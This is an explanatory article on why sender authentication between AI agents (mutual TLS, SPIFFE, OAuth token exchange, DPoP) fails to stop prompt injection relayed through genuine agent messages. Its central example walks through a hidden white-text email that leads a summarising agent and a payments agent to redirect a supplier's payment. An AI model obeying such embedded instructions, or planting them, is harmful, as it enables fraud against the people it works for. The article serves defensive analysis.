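# Why authenticating the sender does not stop attacks carried in messages between AI agents

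## Language agents, their messages and the ways they are attacked

An AI agent is a program in which a language model decides which steps to take and calls tools to carry them out. A tool is any function the program can run at the model's request, such as a web search, a database query or a bank transfer. Agents also work in groups, where one might read documents while another has permission to spend money. They send each other requests and results as messages, and agents permitted to do this are called peer agents.

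Computer networks have long protected messages by authentication, which means checking that a message comes from the person, program or organisation it names. This check does not stop an attacker's request from spreading between agents. A genuine agent with all the right permissions can read a web page or an email that an attacker wrote, then pass the attacker's request to a peer in its own message. That message passes authentication because it comes from the agent it names, and the peer might act on the request because of how agents take in text.

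### The agent loop

Bolin (2026) describes the cycle for Codex, OpenAI's coding agent, in *Unrolling the Codex agent loop*. The program first assembles a prompt, the text it will give the model, which includes the user's request. It converts the prompt into tokens, integers that each stand for an entry in the model's vocabulary. The model produces more tokens, which the program converts back into text. If that text is an answer for the user, the cycle ends. Otherwise it is a request to call a tool, for example to list the files in a folder. The program runs the tool, appends the output to the prompt and queries the model again. A single user request can set off hundreds of tool calls.

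The prompt usually grows with each step. In Codex, each new prompt normally begins with an exact copy of the previous one, which saves computation, and when the user types a follow-up, the earlier conversation is included again. The text the model is given at any moment is its context, and the context window is the maximum number of tokens it can handle in one query. When the text approaches that limit, Codex replaces the history with a shorter version. Until then, a sentence that a tool returned at the third step is still in the context at the fortieth, when the model is choosing an unrelated action.

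Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026), in *AI Agents, Conversations, and Information Flow*, describe the same process mathematically. Call the texts that the program sends to the model $p_1, p_2, \dots$ and the model's responses $r_1, r_2, \dots$. The model draws each new response from a probability distribution that depends on everything so far:

$$r_{i+1} \sim P(\,\cdot \mid p_1 + r_1 + \dots + p_i + r_i + p_{i+1})$$

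The plus sign joins texts end to end. The human's instruction is normally in $p_1$, while a later $p$ may hold the result of a tool call. Both are to the right of the bar, in one string. The formula has no separate slots for instructions and for the material to work on.

### Orders and data in one stream

Partway through a task, an agent's context typically holds the developer's standing instructions (the system prompt), descriptions of the available tools, the user's request, documents, tool results and messages from other agents. Developers label these by source. Codex, for example, gives the items in its initial prompt a role, and Bolin lists four in decreasing order of priority: system, developer, user and assistant (the model's own output). Agents commonly have a further role for tool output, which the model should use as information and never obey. But the labels are tokens in the same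 stream as the text they label. The model has learned in training to give them weight, but there is no guarantee that it will.

*Prompt Injection as Role Confusion* (Ye, Cui and Hadfield-Menell, 2026) tested whether models identify the source of a text by its role label or by how it sounds. The researchers put passages of ordinary web text under five different role labels and trained a simple classifier to tell from a model's internal activity which label was used. Since the passages were the same under every label, the classifier could only pick up the effect of the label. They then applied it to real messages that users had written to chatbots, relabelled as tool output. If the models relied only on labels, the classifier should have identified these messages as tool output. Instead, across four models, it gave "user" an average probability of 76 to 88 percent and "tool" no more than 20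 percent. So these models relied mostly on how a text sounded. The largest had about 120 billion parameters, and the result may not carry over to the strongest commercial systems.

Labels still affect how likely an attack is to succeed, but designers cannot rely on them as a security boundary. *Same Bytes, Different Authority* (Zhan, Song and colleagues, 2026) found that on three of four open-weight model families, malicious instructions wrapped in forged role markers succeeded far less often when the server encoded those markers as ordinary text.

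Older software has had a similar problem. Schneier (2024), in *LLMs' Data-Control Path Insecurity*, traces many security flaws to the mixing of data with commands. In an SQL injection attack, an attacker types part of a database command into a web form, a careless program pastes it into a query, and the database runs it. Programmers can fully prevent this attack with parameterised queries, in which the program fixes the structure of the command first and supplies the user's input separately, so the database never treats the input as a command.

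David C, a technical director at the UK's National Cyber Security Centre, warned in December 2025 in *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)* that prompt injection may never have a cure like the one for SQL injection. A database is designed to handle commands and values differently, whereas a model processes all of its input the same way, by predicting the next token. *Adaptive Evaluation of Out-of-Band Defenses Against Prompt Injection in LLM Agents* (2026) attributes the difference to grammar. SQL's grammar lets a parser find where the command stops and the value begins, but an English sentence has no such boundary. The paper concludes that developers must enforce the separation outside the model.

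It isn't even clear what a clean separation between instructions and data would consist of, and *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026) lists the question among its open research problems. Forbidding the model to follow any instruction in text labelled as data, a popular answer, would rule out a good deal of useful work. If a user asks an agent to carry out the to-do list in a document, the agent has to find the instructions in the data and decide which of them to follow. Messages from peers are arguably harder still, because they are supposed to contain requests, and an agent that ignored them all to protect itself would be of no use to its peers.

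Some researchers are trying to change the models. *Multi-Stream LLMs* (2026) describes versions of two Qwen models, with 4 and 7 billion parameters, that take in the system prompt, the user's input and the model's own response as separate streams. It reports that these versions resist malicious instructions better, without any training on attacks. The result is encouraging, but the models are small and experimental, and the paper describes modern language models as having no separation of privilege between inputs.

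### Prompt injection, direct and indirect

Prompt injection, a term that dates from 2022, is text that makes a model follow an attacker's instructions. In the direct form, the attacker types the text into the chat box. In the indirect form, the attacker plants it in something the model will read later, without touching the system. In David C's example, a recruiter uses a model to score CVs, and a candidate hides a line in their CV telling the model to approve it. An injection can do more harm when the model has more tools. *Careful adoption of agentic AI services*, which the Australian Signals Directorate wrote with American, British, Canadian and New Zealand agencies, describes phishing emails that get an email-monitoring agent to download malware.

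Systems with several agents are also open to inter-agent injection, which is prompt injection that reaches an agent in a message from another agent. Paul and Nandy (2026), in *Beyond Single-Model Injection*, treat it as a separate category and assume that the attacker controls some content that at least one agent processes, but controls none of the agents. They describe a group of six agents in which one checks compliance. That agent receives a tool result containing an instruction to approve every request, works the instruction into its reasoning, and sends a tainted approval to the orchestrator, the agent that hands out the tasks. The orchestrator trusts the compliance agent and forwards the approval without checking it again. Filters placed where user input enters the system never inspect this internal message. The orchestrator cannot easily tell injected instructions from legitimate peer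 messages by itself, since both reach it through the same text channel.

### MCP and Agent2Agent

Two open protocols now standardise much of this traffic. The Model Context Protocol (MCP) carries an agent's calls to tools and data sources and returns the results. Agent2Agent (A2A) carries tasks and messages from one agent to another and returns the second agent's output. The two are often used together, as when an agent receives a task over A2A and calls MCP tools to complete it.

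In the current version of the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a tool call is a single web request that names the tool and its arguments. The example in the protocol's *2026-07-28 release candidate* (2026) calls a search tool with the query "otters". The tool's reply goes into the agent's context like any other text. Tool descriptions go in too, so whoever runs an MCP server adds text to the prompt before the agent calls any tool. MCP is widely used, and Anthropic's *Bringing MCP 2026-07-28 to Claude* (2026) put downloads of the protocol's software kits at more than 400 million a month.

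Google released A2A, the newer protocol, in April 2025. A year later, the Linux Foundation's *A2A Protocol Surpasses 150 Organizations, Lands in Major Cloud Platforms* (2026) reported production use in supply chains, financial services, insurance and IT operations. Ghumare (2026), in *A2A v1.0*, summarizes the protocol as four objects. An Agent Card is a published description of an agent, with its name, skills, network addresses and login requirements. A Task is a unit of work with a state, such as "working" or "completed". A Message consists of parts, which can be text, raw bytes, a web address or structured data. An Artifact is the output of a task.

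A2A treats the agent at the other end as opaque, so the caller can't see its tools, memory, model or plan. That makes sense between companies that don't want to expose their internals, but it also means that the receiver of a message generally can't tell what the sender had been reading when it wrote the message. In Ghumare's sample code, the calling agent sends its words in a Message with the role "user", and a sample server extracts the text from an incoming Message and passes it directly to its own agent. "User" is A2A's word for the calling side, and each developer can decide how to present the text to the model. However the developer does it, the peer's words end up in the receiving model's context alongside everything else.

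### The Reader and Payments example

Suppose a company runs two agents, the Reader and Payments. The Reader has access to the mailbox that suppliers write to, and summarises their emails for Payments, which holds the suppliers' bank details and can send money. Payments never opens emails itself, and the Reader, which is exposed to messages from strangers, cannot send money. The Reader authenticates itself whenever it sends a message, and Payments accepts summaries only from the Reader.

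Suppose an attacker wants to divert a supplier's next payment to their own account. They can try to do this in four ways through the channel between the two agents.

| Attack | What the attacker needs | What arrives at Payments |
| --- | --- | --- |
| Impersonating the sender | A network connection to Payments | A message from the attacker's program under the Reader's name |
| Altering a message | A position on the path between the agents | The Reader's message with a different account number |
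| Stealing a credential | The Reader's secret key or token | A message from the attacker's program with the Reader's real credential |
| Putting harmful content into a genuine message | An email address that the Reader monitors | The Reader's own message, exactly as the Reader sent it |

Besides altering messages, attackers can replay them by recording a genuine message and sending it again, perhaps to trigger the same payment twice. The Australian Signals Directorate and its co-authors warn that attackers can also steal credentials such as keys and tokens when organisations leave them unchanged, share them between several agents or protect them poorly.

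The last attack needs far less than the others. The attacker doesn't have to break into anything or intercept any traffic, and can work from an ordinary email account. It goes like this:

1. The attacker writes to the suppliers' mailbox. The email looks like a routine question about an invoice, and hidden in it is a request to change the supplier's bank account.
2. The Reader's program fetches the email with a tool call and appends it to the context, where the request sits in the same stream as the Reader's real instructions.
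3. The Reader's model writes its summary and includes the change of account as something the supplier has asked for.
4. The Reader sends the summary to Payments in its own authenticated message.
5. Payments confirms that the message comes from the Reader and adds the text to its context. Its model calls the tool that updates bank details, and the next payment goes to the attacker.

The government agencies describe a similar hypothetical case in their guidance. An organisation gives a procurement agent broad access to its financial systems, email and contracts, and over time other agents come to trust that agent's output. An attacker gets in through a minor tool in the agent's workflow, changes contracts and approves payments. Because all these actions run under a trusted agent's identity, they trigger no alerts and the audit logs look legitimate.

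## What authenticating an agent proves and which attacks it stops

Security engineers already have good tools against an attacker who impersonates the Reader, alters its messages or steals its credentials. Suppose the company has installed every identity check that current guidance recommends. A clerk called Maria has asked the Reader to work through the morning's supplier emails, and it is about to send its summary to Payments.

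### Giving the Reader an identity

A program has no fingerprint or phone to prove who it is, so something has to give it an identity when it starts. The quick way is to paste a secret key into its configuration file, but anyone who can read the file can then pose as the program. SPIFFE (Secure Production Identity Framework for Everyone) is an open standard that avoids this by issuing cryptographic identities to running programs, called workload identities. *Accelerating the Adoption of Software and AI Agent Identity and Authorization* (Booth, Fisher and colleagues, 2026), a concept paper from the US National Institute of Standards and Technology (NIST), lists SPIFFE and its implementation SPIRE as one way to identify and authenticate agents.

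SPIRE identifies the Reader from facts about its running process, so the Reader needs no secret to begin with. When the Reader starts, it requests an identity from a SPIRE process on the same machine. SPIRE uses the operating system to identify the requesting process and collects properties such as the account it runs under, its container image or a hash (a short digital fingerprint) of its program file. If these match the properties an administrator has already recorded for the Reader, the Reader receives a private key and a certificate that ties its name, such as `spiffe://acme.example/reader`, to the corresponding public key. By default the certificate expires after an hour, and SPIRE replaces it automatically.

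The certificate proves that, when SPIRE issued it, a process with the registered properties was running on a known machine. If those properties include the hash, it also proves that the process started from the approved program file. The Australian Signals Directorate and its five partner agencies recommend this kind of check, in which agents prove that they are running unmodified code. The check is very useful for a conventional service, because the code largely determines what the service will do with an input. But the Reader's behaviour also depends on the text in its context, which the hash doesn't cover. Reading the attacker's email doesn't change the Reader's program file, so the Reader would still pass the check afterwards.

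### Opening the connection

The Reader now connects to Payments over TLS, the protocol that secures ordinary web traffic. Usually only the server proves its identity on the web, but in mutual TLS both sides do. Each sends its certificate and uses its private key to sign a digest of the opening messages, called the handshake. The other side checks the signature and confirms that the certificate is in date and comes from an issuer it trusts. During the handshake the two programs also agree on fresh secret keys, which they use to encrypt everything afterwards and to detect changes. The encryption of each piece of data also depends on its position in the sequence.

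Payments has now verified that whatever is at the other end of this connection holds the Reader's private key, and it can detect any change to the data in transit. If an attacker on the path edits the account number, the integrity check fails and Payments drops the connection. Replaying recorded traffic also fails, because each new connection uses new keys and the old connection is already past those sequence numbers. TLS 1.3's optional early data feature lacks full protection against replay, so a payment service should leave it off.

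TLS protects only against copies made on the network. If the Reader's own program times out and sends the same request twice, TLS accepts both copies, and Payments needs a unique identifier in the message to recognise the second as a duplicate. The agencies' guidance includes integrity and freshness checks on the messages themselves, which would cover this case. The protection also ends where the TLS connection ends. Many companies decrypt traffic at a proxy in front of the service, and the proxy then forwards the message with the sender's name in a header. Payments then never receives the Reader's proof and has to rely on the proxy to have checked it.

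### Acting on Maria's behalf

Mutual TLS identifies the connecting agent to Payments, but not the user that agent is working for. The company could get round this by giving the Reader Maria's password, but then nobody could tell from the logs whether Maria or the agent did something. NIST's *Back to the Future*, a blog post from August 2026, describes sharing personal and company credentials with agents as a common pattern that leaves gaps in accountability.

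OAuth 2.0, the usual standard for delegated access, has a better answer. An authorisation server issues access tokens, which are short-lived records of what the holder may do and where. Under an extension called token exchange (RFC 8693), the Reader sends the server one token that represents Maria, which it received when she signed in, and another that represents itself. It also names the service it needs to reach. The server verifies both tokens, checks that the Reader may act for Maria and returns a new token. Decoded, the main part might look like this:

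```json
{
  "iss": "acme-login",
  "sub": "maria",
  "act": { "sub": "spiffe://acme.example/reader" },
  "aud": "payments",
  "scope": "supplier-requests",
  "exp": 1796468400,
  "cnf": { "x5t#S256": "<hash of the Reader's certificate>" }
}
```

The subject (`sub`) is Maria, the actor (`act`) is the Reader, and the audience (`aud`) is Payments, the only service that should accept this token. The number after `exp` is the expiry time. Payments checks the authorisation server's signature, the audience and the expiry to confirm that the server allowed the Reader to send it supplier requests for Maria until that time. These checks don't show that Maria wanted any particular request. She asked the Reader to go through the mail, but until the token expires, the Reader can attach her name to whatever it sends.

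Recording the user can still prevent harm. The agencies describe a hypothetical agent that installs software patches and has broad write access to company devices. An insider outside the privileged IT group asks it to apply a patch and clean up the firewall logs. The agent deletes the logs because its own permissions allow it. If the agent had carried a token with the insider as the subject, the system holding the logs could have refused. The attack on Payments could also have been refused if Maria had no right to change bank details and Payments passed her authority along when it tried to change them. But the person who asks an agent to handle supplier email may well be allowed to update supplier accounts as part of their job.

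Token exchange can also record a chain of actors. If Payments exchanges the token again to call a bank, the new token can list Payments as the current actor and the Reader as an earlier one. Under RFC 8693, the bank may use only the subject and the current actor for access control, and earlier actors are included only for information. Even if the bank checked the whole chain, it would find only principals that had acted under delegated authority. The stranger who wrote the email never had that authority, so they don't appear in the chain.

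### Tying the token to its holder

An ordinary access token is a bearer token, so anyone who obtains it can use it. NIST says that bearer tokens and fixed API keys (secret strings that give a program access to a service) don't prove identity, and that people often leave them unprotected in configuration files and logs. Agents make this worse because they carry credentials across many tools and networks. NIST attributes many substantial security incidents to lost or misused long-lived tokens.

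The remedy is to make the token useless without a private key. With mutual TLS, the authorisation server puts a hash of the Reader's certificate in the token's `cnf` field. Payments compares it with the certificate on the connection and rejects the request if they differ. SPIRE replaces certificates every hour or so, and a token tied to the old certificate stops working on a connection that uses the new one, so tokens have to be short-lived too, or the Reader has to be able to fetch new ones easily.

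The alternative is DPoP (Demonstrating Proof of Possession, RFC 9449), which works without client certificates. The token contains a hash of a public key, and the Reader sends a signed proof with each request. The proof contains the request's web address and method, the time, a unique identifier and a hash of the token. Payments checks the signature and compares these details with the request it received. It can also store recent identifiers and reject repeats.

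Either method proves that the sender holds both the token and the matching private key, so a thief who finds the token in a log file cannot use it. NIST judges that DPoP can mitigate many token theft scenarios, and "many" seems right, since an attacker who controls the Reader's machine can use the key to sign anything. DPoP's proof also doesn't cover the body of the request, so the signature would still be valid if someone changed the account number in the message. The company needs TLS to prevent that.

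### The registry and the policy decision

Payments next looks the Reader up in the company's registry of agents. The agencies recommend that organisations tie each identity in the registry to its authorised roles, deny access to any agent or key missing from it, and regularly compare it with the agents that are running. A successful lookup proves that someone approved this agent for this role and has not withdrawn the approval. It catches an agent that a developer launched without permission, or one that the company retired but forgot to switch off. How reliable the approval is depends on who can add entries. The agencies warn about "squatting", where attackers publish malicious agents under names that resemble legitimate ones, and a registry that anyone can add to could include those as well.

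The remaining question is whether the Reader may make this request now. NIST's *Zero Trust Architecture* (SP 800-207, from 2020) is the standard account of how to decide this. Zero trust is a security approach that checks each request and doesn't grant access just because the requester is inside the network. In SP 800-207, a policy decision point decides whether to allow the request, and a policy enforcement point in front of the resource lets it through or blocks it. The inputs to the decision include the requester's identity, the resource, the condition of the requester's machine, the organisation's rules and reports of current threats.

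SP 800-207 describes access as granted for one session at a time. The agencies go further and recommend a central policy decision for every request. They give the hypothetical example of a support agent that receives broad access at start-up and keeps relying on it. An attacker takes over a third-party scheduling component and uses it to call sensitive account functions. Checking each call would have given the organisation a chance to refuse it.

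The decision about the Reader is easy because it is a known agent on a healthy machine, acting for a current employee, and its role is to send supplier summaries to Payments. An approval proves that the company's rules permit this principal to take this action on this resource at this moment. SP 800-207 also allows for contextual decisions, which take recent behaviour into account. A sudden burst of messages might then arouse suspicion, but one summary on a normal morning would not. When Payments later calls the tool that updates bank details, that call needs a second decision, this time about Payments, whose job includes making such updates.

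### Signed agent cards and MCP authorisation

A2A and MCP both rely on these existing standards and add a few rules. In A2A, the Reader can find Payments through the description published in its Agent Card. A false card could direct the Reader to an attacker's server, so A2A lets the publisher sign the card. The publisher puts the card into a standard form, so that differences in spacing or field order don't matter, and signs the result as a JSON Web Signature, a common format for signed data. The Reader rebuilds the same form and checks the signature with the publisher's public key.

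A valid signature proves that the key's holder published the card and that nobody has changed it since. The Reader still needs a trustworthy source for the key. A2A also makes signing optional. The signature does not show that the description is accurate, since a publisher can sign exaggerated claims about an agent's skills.

The signature on the card doesn't cover the messages the agents exchange later. A2A authenticates the senders of those messages with the methods listed in the card, which can include OAuth and mutual TLS. The caller's identity is in the surrounding web request, not in the A2A message. So when a server extracts the text of a message and gives it to a model, as the sample code from the last section does, the model gets no evidence of who sent it unless the developer passes that on.

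Authorisation in MCP is optional and based on OAuth. Booth and colleagues note that it follows the draft of version 2.1. The June 2025 revision made MCP servers OAuth resource servers, which accept tokens issued by an authorisation server. An agent must state which MCP server it wants a token for, and that server must refuse tokens meant for any other. MCP also forbids servers from passing an agent's token on to another service. Without these rules, the operator of a malicious weather tool could try an agent's token at the agent's bank. Under these rules, an accepted token proves that an authorisation server approved this client for this MCP server. It proves nothing about the text that the tool then returns, which still enters the agent's context.

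### What official bodies recommend

The Reader's request took a path close to the one the six agencies set out in May 2026. They recommend that developers build each agent as a distinct principal with its own keys or certificates, and use mutual TLS for all calls between agents and from agents to services. They also want organisations to replace permanent secrets with ones that expire when the job is done, and to require a fresh cryptographic proof before every privileged call.

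The agencies also recommend filters for prompt injection and human approval for high-impact actions, so they don't present identity as a complete defence. Their broadest advice is that organisations should use agents only for low-risk, non-sensitive tasks, which would rule out an agent like Payments.

NIST is at an earlier stage. Booth and colleagues published their concept paper in February 2026 to gather comments on a possible project to apply existing identity standards to agents. Most of it concerns identification, authorisation, delegation and logging, but it also includes questions about how to prevent prompt injection and limit the damage afterwards. One proposed area of work is tracking the provenance of prompts and input data, so that an organisation can consider it when deciding what an agent may do. This goes beyond identity and is the part of the paper most relevant to the attacker's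 email. The first phase is limited to agents inside an enterprise and excludes external agents from untrusted sources.

The paper received more than 600 formal responses, according to *Advancing Standards for Agent Identity* (Galluzzo, 2026), the description of a November conference session. NIST's August blog post drew on those responses to argue that developers in a hurry are repeating old mistakes, such as sharing credentials and granting overly broad access, and that the standards to avoid them largely exist. The post doesn't discuss prompt injection or the tracking of data flows. In September, NIST (2026) finalised its guidelines on protecting access tokens from misuse, and in October *Design Tenets for Agent Identity Management Systems* (Booth, 2026) continued the blog series.

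*Software and SI Agent Identity and Authorization*, a page from NIST's National Cybersecurity Center of Excellence (NCCoE), reports that by mid-November the project had also released a summary of the comments and opened an online resource hub. ("SI" stands for super intelligence, the term the NCCoE now uses on that page for AI.) The project was still soliciting comments then. Galluzzo says the demonstration of agent identity and authorisation is planned, so the practice guide, which the concept paper describes as the project's main product, probably won't be published soon.

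Engineers writing the underlying protocols haven't settled on a design either. Flanagan (2026), in *Do We Need New Protocols, or Better Architecture?*, compares three proposals for agent authorisation. Two share the name AAuth but were developed independently. One of these is now an input to work at the OpenID Foundation, and the other would extend OAuth. The third, AIMS, is under discussion in a working group of the Internet Engineering Task Force, which standardises internet protocols.

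### Whether mutual TLS provides non-repudiation

Mutual TLS does not provide non-repudiation, which is evidence that would convince a third party that someone sent a message, even if they deny it. The agencies nevertheless recommend that organisations use mutual TLS "to ensure non-repudiation".

Suppose different companies run the Reader and Payments, and the money has gone to the attacker. Payments' operator shows an auditor a log in which the Reader asks for the new account number. The Reader's operator denies that its agent sent the request. Each side signed only the handshake, and both then held all the secret keys used to encrypt the messages that followed. Payments could therefore have produced any message that the Reader could have encrypted. Even with the keys and a complete recording of the connection, the auditor could not tell a real message from one that Payments' operator made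 up afterwards.

A full record of the handshake would show the auditor that the holder of the Reader's key had opened a connection to Payments, because the Reader's signature in the handshake covers both certificates. It would not show what the two programs sent each other afterwards. Companies rarely keep such records, and without them the auditor has only the logs that each side wrote about itself.

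To get non-repudiation, the Reader has to sign the message. It would sign the text together with the recipient, the time and a unique identifier, and Payments would store the result. The auditor can check the signature with the Reader's public key, and Payments could not have produced it because Payments doesn't have the Reader's private key. Suitable standards include JSON Web Signature and HTTP Message Signatures (RFC 9421). With certificates that last an hour, the companies would also have to archive old certificates and keep reliable evidence of when the Reader signed.

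Elsewhere in the same guidance, the agencies also recommend cryptographic signatures on authorised commands and instructions. An organisation that followed all of their advice would therefore have the evidence it needs, but one that stopped at mutual TLS would have less than it had been led to expect. Booth and colleagues are more careful and list non-repudiation as an open question, including how to connect an agent's actions to a human's authorisation. A log of human approvals may not show that a person meant to authorise an action, because people who get too many approval requests start to click "allow" by reflex, as NIST warns in its August post.

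A signature on the Reader's summary would settle the dispute between the two companies. The auditor would conclude, correctly, that the Reader had asked for the new account number.

### Attacks and controls

If the company sets everything up properly, the identity checks stop impersonation, tampering, replay and the use of stolen tokens. The right-hand column below lists what an attacker would need to succeed anyway, which in most rows is hard to get.

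| Attack | What stops it | What the attacker would still need |
| --- | --- | --- |
| Impersonating the Reader | Workload identity with mutual TLS | The Reader's private key, or control of the system that issues certificates |
| Running an unapproved or retired agent | Registry lookup | A way to add or restore a registry entry |
| Publishing a false Agent Card for Payments | A signed card, checked against a key the Reader already trusts | The publisher's signing key |
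| Altering a message on the way | TLS, or a signature on the message | Control of a proxy that decrypts the traffic, or the Reader's key if it signs its messages |
| Replaying a message | TLS for copies made on the network, unique identifiers for other copies | A receiver that doesn't keep track of identifiers |
| Using a stolen token | Binding the token to a key, by mutual TLS or DPoP | The matching private key, or control of the Reader's machine |
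| Using a token at a different service | Audience check | A service that skips the check |
| Exceeding a user's rights through an agent | Token exchange with a policy decision for each request | A user who already has those rights |
| Putting harmful content into a genuine message | None of these checks, if the request is within the rights of the agents and the user | An email address that the Reader monitors |

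## Why a genuine sender says little about the content of a message

Payments has now confirmed that the summary came from the Reader, that the Reader may send it, and that the token names Maria. None of these identity checks justifies the step from "the Reader asked for a new account number" to "the account number should change". Researchers at Digital Equipment Corporation formalized this kind of step in the early 1990s, while designing an authentication system for networked computers.

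### From "A says s" to s

Lampson, Abadi and colleagues (1992), in *Authentication in Distributed Systems*, start from a guard that examines every request to use a file or device. Authentication answers the question "Who said this?" and authorisation answers "Who is trusted to access this?" They write an answer to the first question as *A says s*, where A is a principal, such as a person or program, and s is a request or a claim. People and programs can reach a computer only through a channel, such as a cryptographic key, so the logic also has to relate channels to the principals that use them. If key K *speaks for* A, written K ⇒ A, then A says whatever K says.

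Payments can use this logic to reason about the summary:

1. K says s, because s arrived over a connection secured with key K.
2. K ⇒ Reader, because a certificate ties the key to the Reader.
3. Therefore the Reader says s.
4. The Reader controls s.
5. Therefore s.

The word "controls" comes from a companion paper of 1993. Abadi, Burrows and colleagues, in *A Calculus for Access Control in Distributed Systems*, define it as

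$$A \text{ controls } s \quad\text{means}\quad (A \text{ says } s) \rightarrow s$$

An access control list, in this logic, is a list of such assertions. Authentication lets Payments conclude only that "the Reader says s". An administrator has to judge separately whether the "controls" premise holds, and if that judgement is wrong, s can be false even though every signature was valid. Lampson and colleagues allow one exception, in which a listener may accept on A's word alone that B speaks for A. This adds no risk, since A could have repeated whatever B says anyway.

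The requirements for controlling s depend on what s is. In an example from Abadi and colleagues, a user says that his files should be deleted, and the system obeys because the files are his. But the logic uses the same notation for factual claims, which a sender can't make true by wishing. Suppose the supplier in the attacker's email is called Harlow Paper, and the Reader reports that Harlow's bank account is now number 4471. This is a claim about a third party, so the Reader controls it only if the Reader would never report it when it was false.

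The Reader cannot meet that condition, because its summary depends on every email in its context and anyone who can write to the mailbox can add one. Payments could safely trust the summary about bank details only if the Reader left out false details whatever the attacker wrote. A conventional program can meet such a requirement. If it copies an invoice total from a fixed field, its developer can work out everything a malicious invoice could change. Nobody can work this out for the Reader, because any sentence in its context might affect any part of its output.

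Lampson and colleagues did allow for trust in programs. An access list can name a program, which the system identifies by a digest of its code. But they use "program" to mean "something that obeys a specification", and this justifies putting it on the list. A digest of the Reader's code identifies its program file, but no specification determines what its model will write after reading a stranger's email.

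A successful injection lets the attacker speak for the Reader through an email, although nobody issued a certificate allowing it. So an administrator who trusts the Reader to control changes of bank details is in practice trusting everyone who knows the mailbox's address. The only limit is how often the Reader's model happens to resist the injected instructions.

### The confused deputy

Attackers were using programs' legitimate permissions against the programs' owners long before language models existed. Hardy's 1988 article *The Confused Deputy* describes an incident from about eleven years earlier at Tymshare, a company that sold time on its computers. Customers could run a compiler there and name a file to receive its debugging output. The compiler also recorded usage statistics in a system directory, so Tymshare had given it permission to write files there. The same directory held the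 company's billing records, in a file called BILL. A customer learned the file's name and gave it as the destination for debugging output. The operating system allowed the write because the compiler had permission, and the compiler overwrote the billing records.

The operating system correctly identified the program asking to open the file as the compiler. Hardy attributes the problem to the compiler having authority from two sources, its own permission and the customer who ran it, with no way to specify which one to use. Checking file names would not have solved this, because some customers might have had legitimate access to SYSX, and a list of forbidden names would have needed an update for every new sensitive file. Tymshare added a way for the compiler to choose between its two authorities, but some applications soon needed more than two.

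Hardy's answer was to use capabilities, unforgeable tokens that each grant a specific right. The customer would give the compiler a capability for the output file instead of a name, so a customer without a capability for BILL could not have made the compiler write to that file.

Payments is a deputy in Hardy's sense. It is allowed to change bank details and the attacker is not, but the attacker supplies the number that Payments writes into the record. In *Delegation Without Trust*, Dantuluri and Sundi (2026) restate the problem for agents: "The agent is authorized; the use is not intended."

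Tymshare's customer typed a file name where a file name belonged, and the compiler followed its code exactly. The attacker who emails the Reader, by contrast, has nowhere to enter a request. The Reader is meant to summarise the email, which becomes a request only because of how the model responds to its wording, so there is no faulty line of code for a developer to find.

The other difference matters more for access control. If the compiler had opened the debugging file with the customer's authority, the operating system would have refused. Limiting Payments to Maria's authority would not prevent the change, because she is allowed to change suppliers' bank details. Making the change is also part of Payments' own job. The rights of the stranger who wrote the email ought to limit the request, but the stranger has no account, token or entry in any access list. Every principal that the system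 knows about has the right to make the request.

*On access control, capabilities, their equivalence, and confused deputy attacks*, by Rajani, Garg and Rezk, gives the first formal definition of a program that is free of confused deputy attacks. It relates this definition to information-flow integrity, which roughly means that untrusted inputs cannot influence what must be trustworthy. What went wrong at Payments is better described as a failure of integrity than as a failure to establish identity, because the attacker influenced a request without making it.

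### How a summary loses the origin of a request

The logic of Lampson and colleagues has a notation for reported speech. "Reader | Harlow says s" means that the Reader says that Harlow says s. They add that this doesn't show that Harlow said it, because the Reader "could be mistaken or lying". To get from there to s, Payments would need two premises:

- The Reader is right about what Harlow said.
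- Harlow controls s.

The premise about Harlow is sensible, since a supplier is the natural authority on its own bank account. The premise about the Reader is false here because a stranger wrote the email. If the message had reached Payments in this form, it would at least have been clear that someone needed to check whether Harlow had really said it.

But the Reader's job is to summarise. Suppose the attacker's email comes from an address that resembles Harlow's and asks whether invoice 2291 has arrived. Below that, in white text on a white background, it states that Harlow's account number is now 4471 and that any summary should mention this. The Reader sends Payments two sentences:

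> Harlow Paper would like confirmation that we received invoice 2291. Its bank account number is now 4471.

The Reader's summary omits the odd address, the hidden text, and the fact that the account number was only a claim in an email. In the notation, "the Reader says that the email says s" has become "the Reader says s". The Reader then sends the summary over its authenticated connection, which gives Payments cryptographic evidence that the summary is the Reader's but no evidence about the email.

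If Harlow really had changed banks and written to say so, the Reader might have sent Payments the same two sentences, word for word. No filter, stronger model or careful human could then tell the honest message from the fraudulent one by examining it. They would need evidence from outside the message, such as the original email or a phone call to Harlow on a number the company already had.

It would be unfair to call this a defect in the Reader, because the company installed it so that Payments would not have to open emails, and any useful summary leaves things out. A developer could instruct the Reader to name the source of every claim, which would help with accidental errors. But the model would write those attributions from a context that includes the attacker's text, so they would also be unverified claims from the Reader. Software outside the model can record origins more reliably by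 attaching labels to data, as later sections describe.

The problem gets worse as a claim passes from one agent to another. Once Payments has written 4471 into the supplier database, another agent that prepares the monthly payments will read it from the company's own records. The claim began in a stranger's email, was repeated in a colleague's report, and is now in an official record, even though each agent authenticated its source correctly.

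### How much a passed check tells the receiver

Authentication can leave the risk almost unchanged. In a hypothetical example, Payments receives 1,000 messages, of which 10 are harmful. Impostors sent 2 of the harmful messages, and genuine peers relayed the other 8. Authentication blocks the 2 from impostors and admits the other 998, so the harmful share falls from 1.0 percent to 0.8 percent.

Bayes' rule gives the general relationship. If H means that a message is harmful, then

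$$\frac{P(H \mid \text{pass})}{P(\text{not } H \mid \text{pass})} = \frac{P(H)}{P(\text{not } H)} \times \frac{P(\text{pass} \mid H)}{P(\text{pass} \mid \text{not } H)}$$

Before the check, the odds that a message was harmful were 10 to 990. Eight in ten harmful messages pass, and so do all the harmless ones. Dividing the first pass rate by the second gives 0.8, so the odds of harm among messages that pass are 8 to 990. If harmful and harmless messages pass equally often, the ratio is 1 and passing does not change the odds. This is the case when the sender check is applied to messages from genuine peers, because all of them pass.

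The benefit of authentication therefore depends on who is sending the harmful messages.

| Harmful messages from impostors | Harmful messages relayed by genuine peers | Harmful share after authentication |
| --- | --- | --- |
| 9 | 1 | 0.1% |
| 5 | 5 | 0.5% |
| 2 | 8 | 0.8% |
| 0 | 10 | 1.0% |

A company with no identity checks might well be in the top row, because its agents are easy to impersonate, and it should certainly add those checks. Once it does, impersonating the Reader will require its private key, while an injection will still require only an email. Attackers will probably then rely more on injection, which would move the company down the table.

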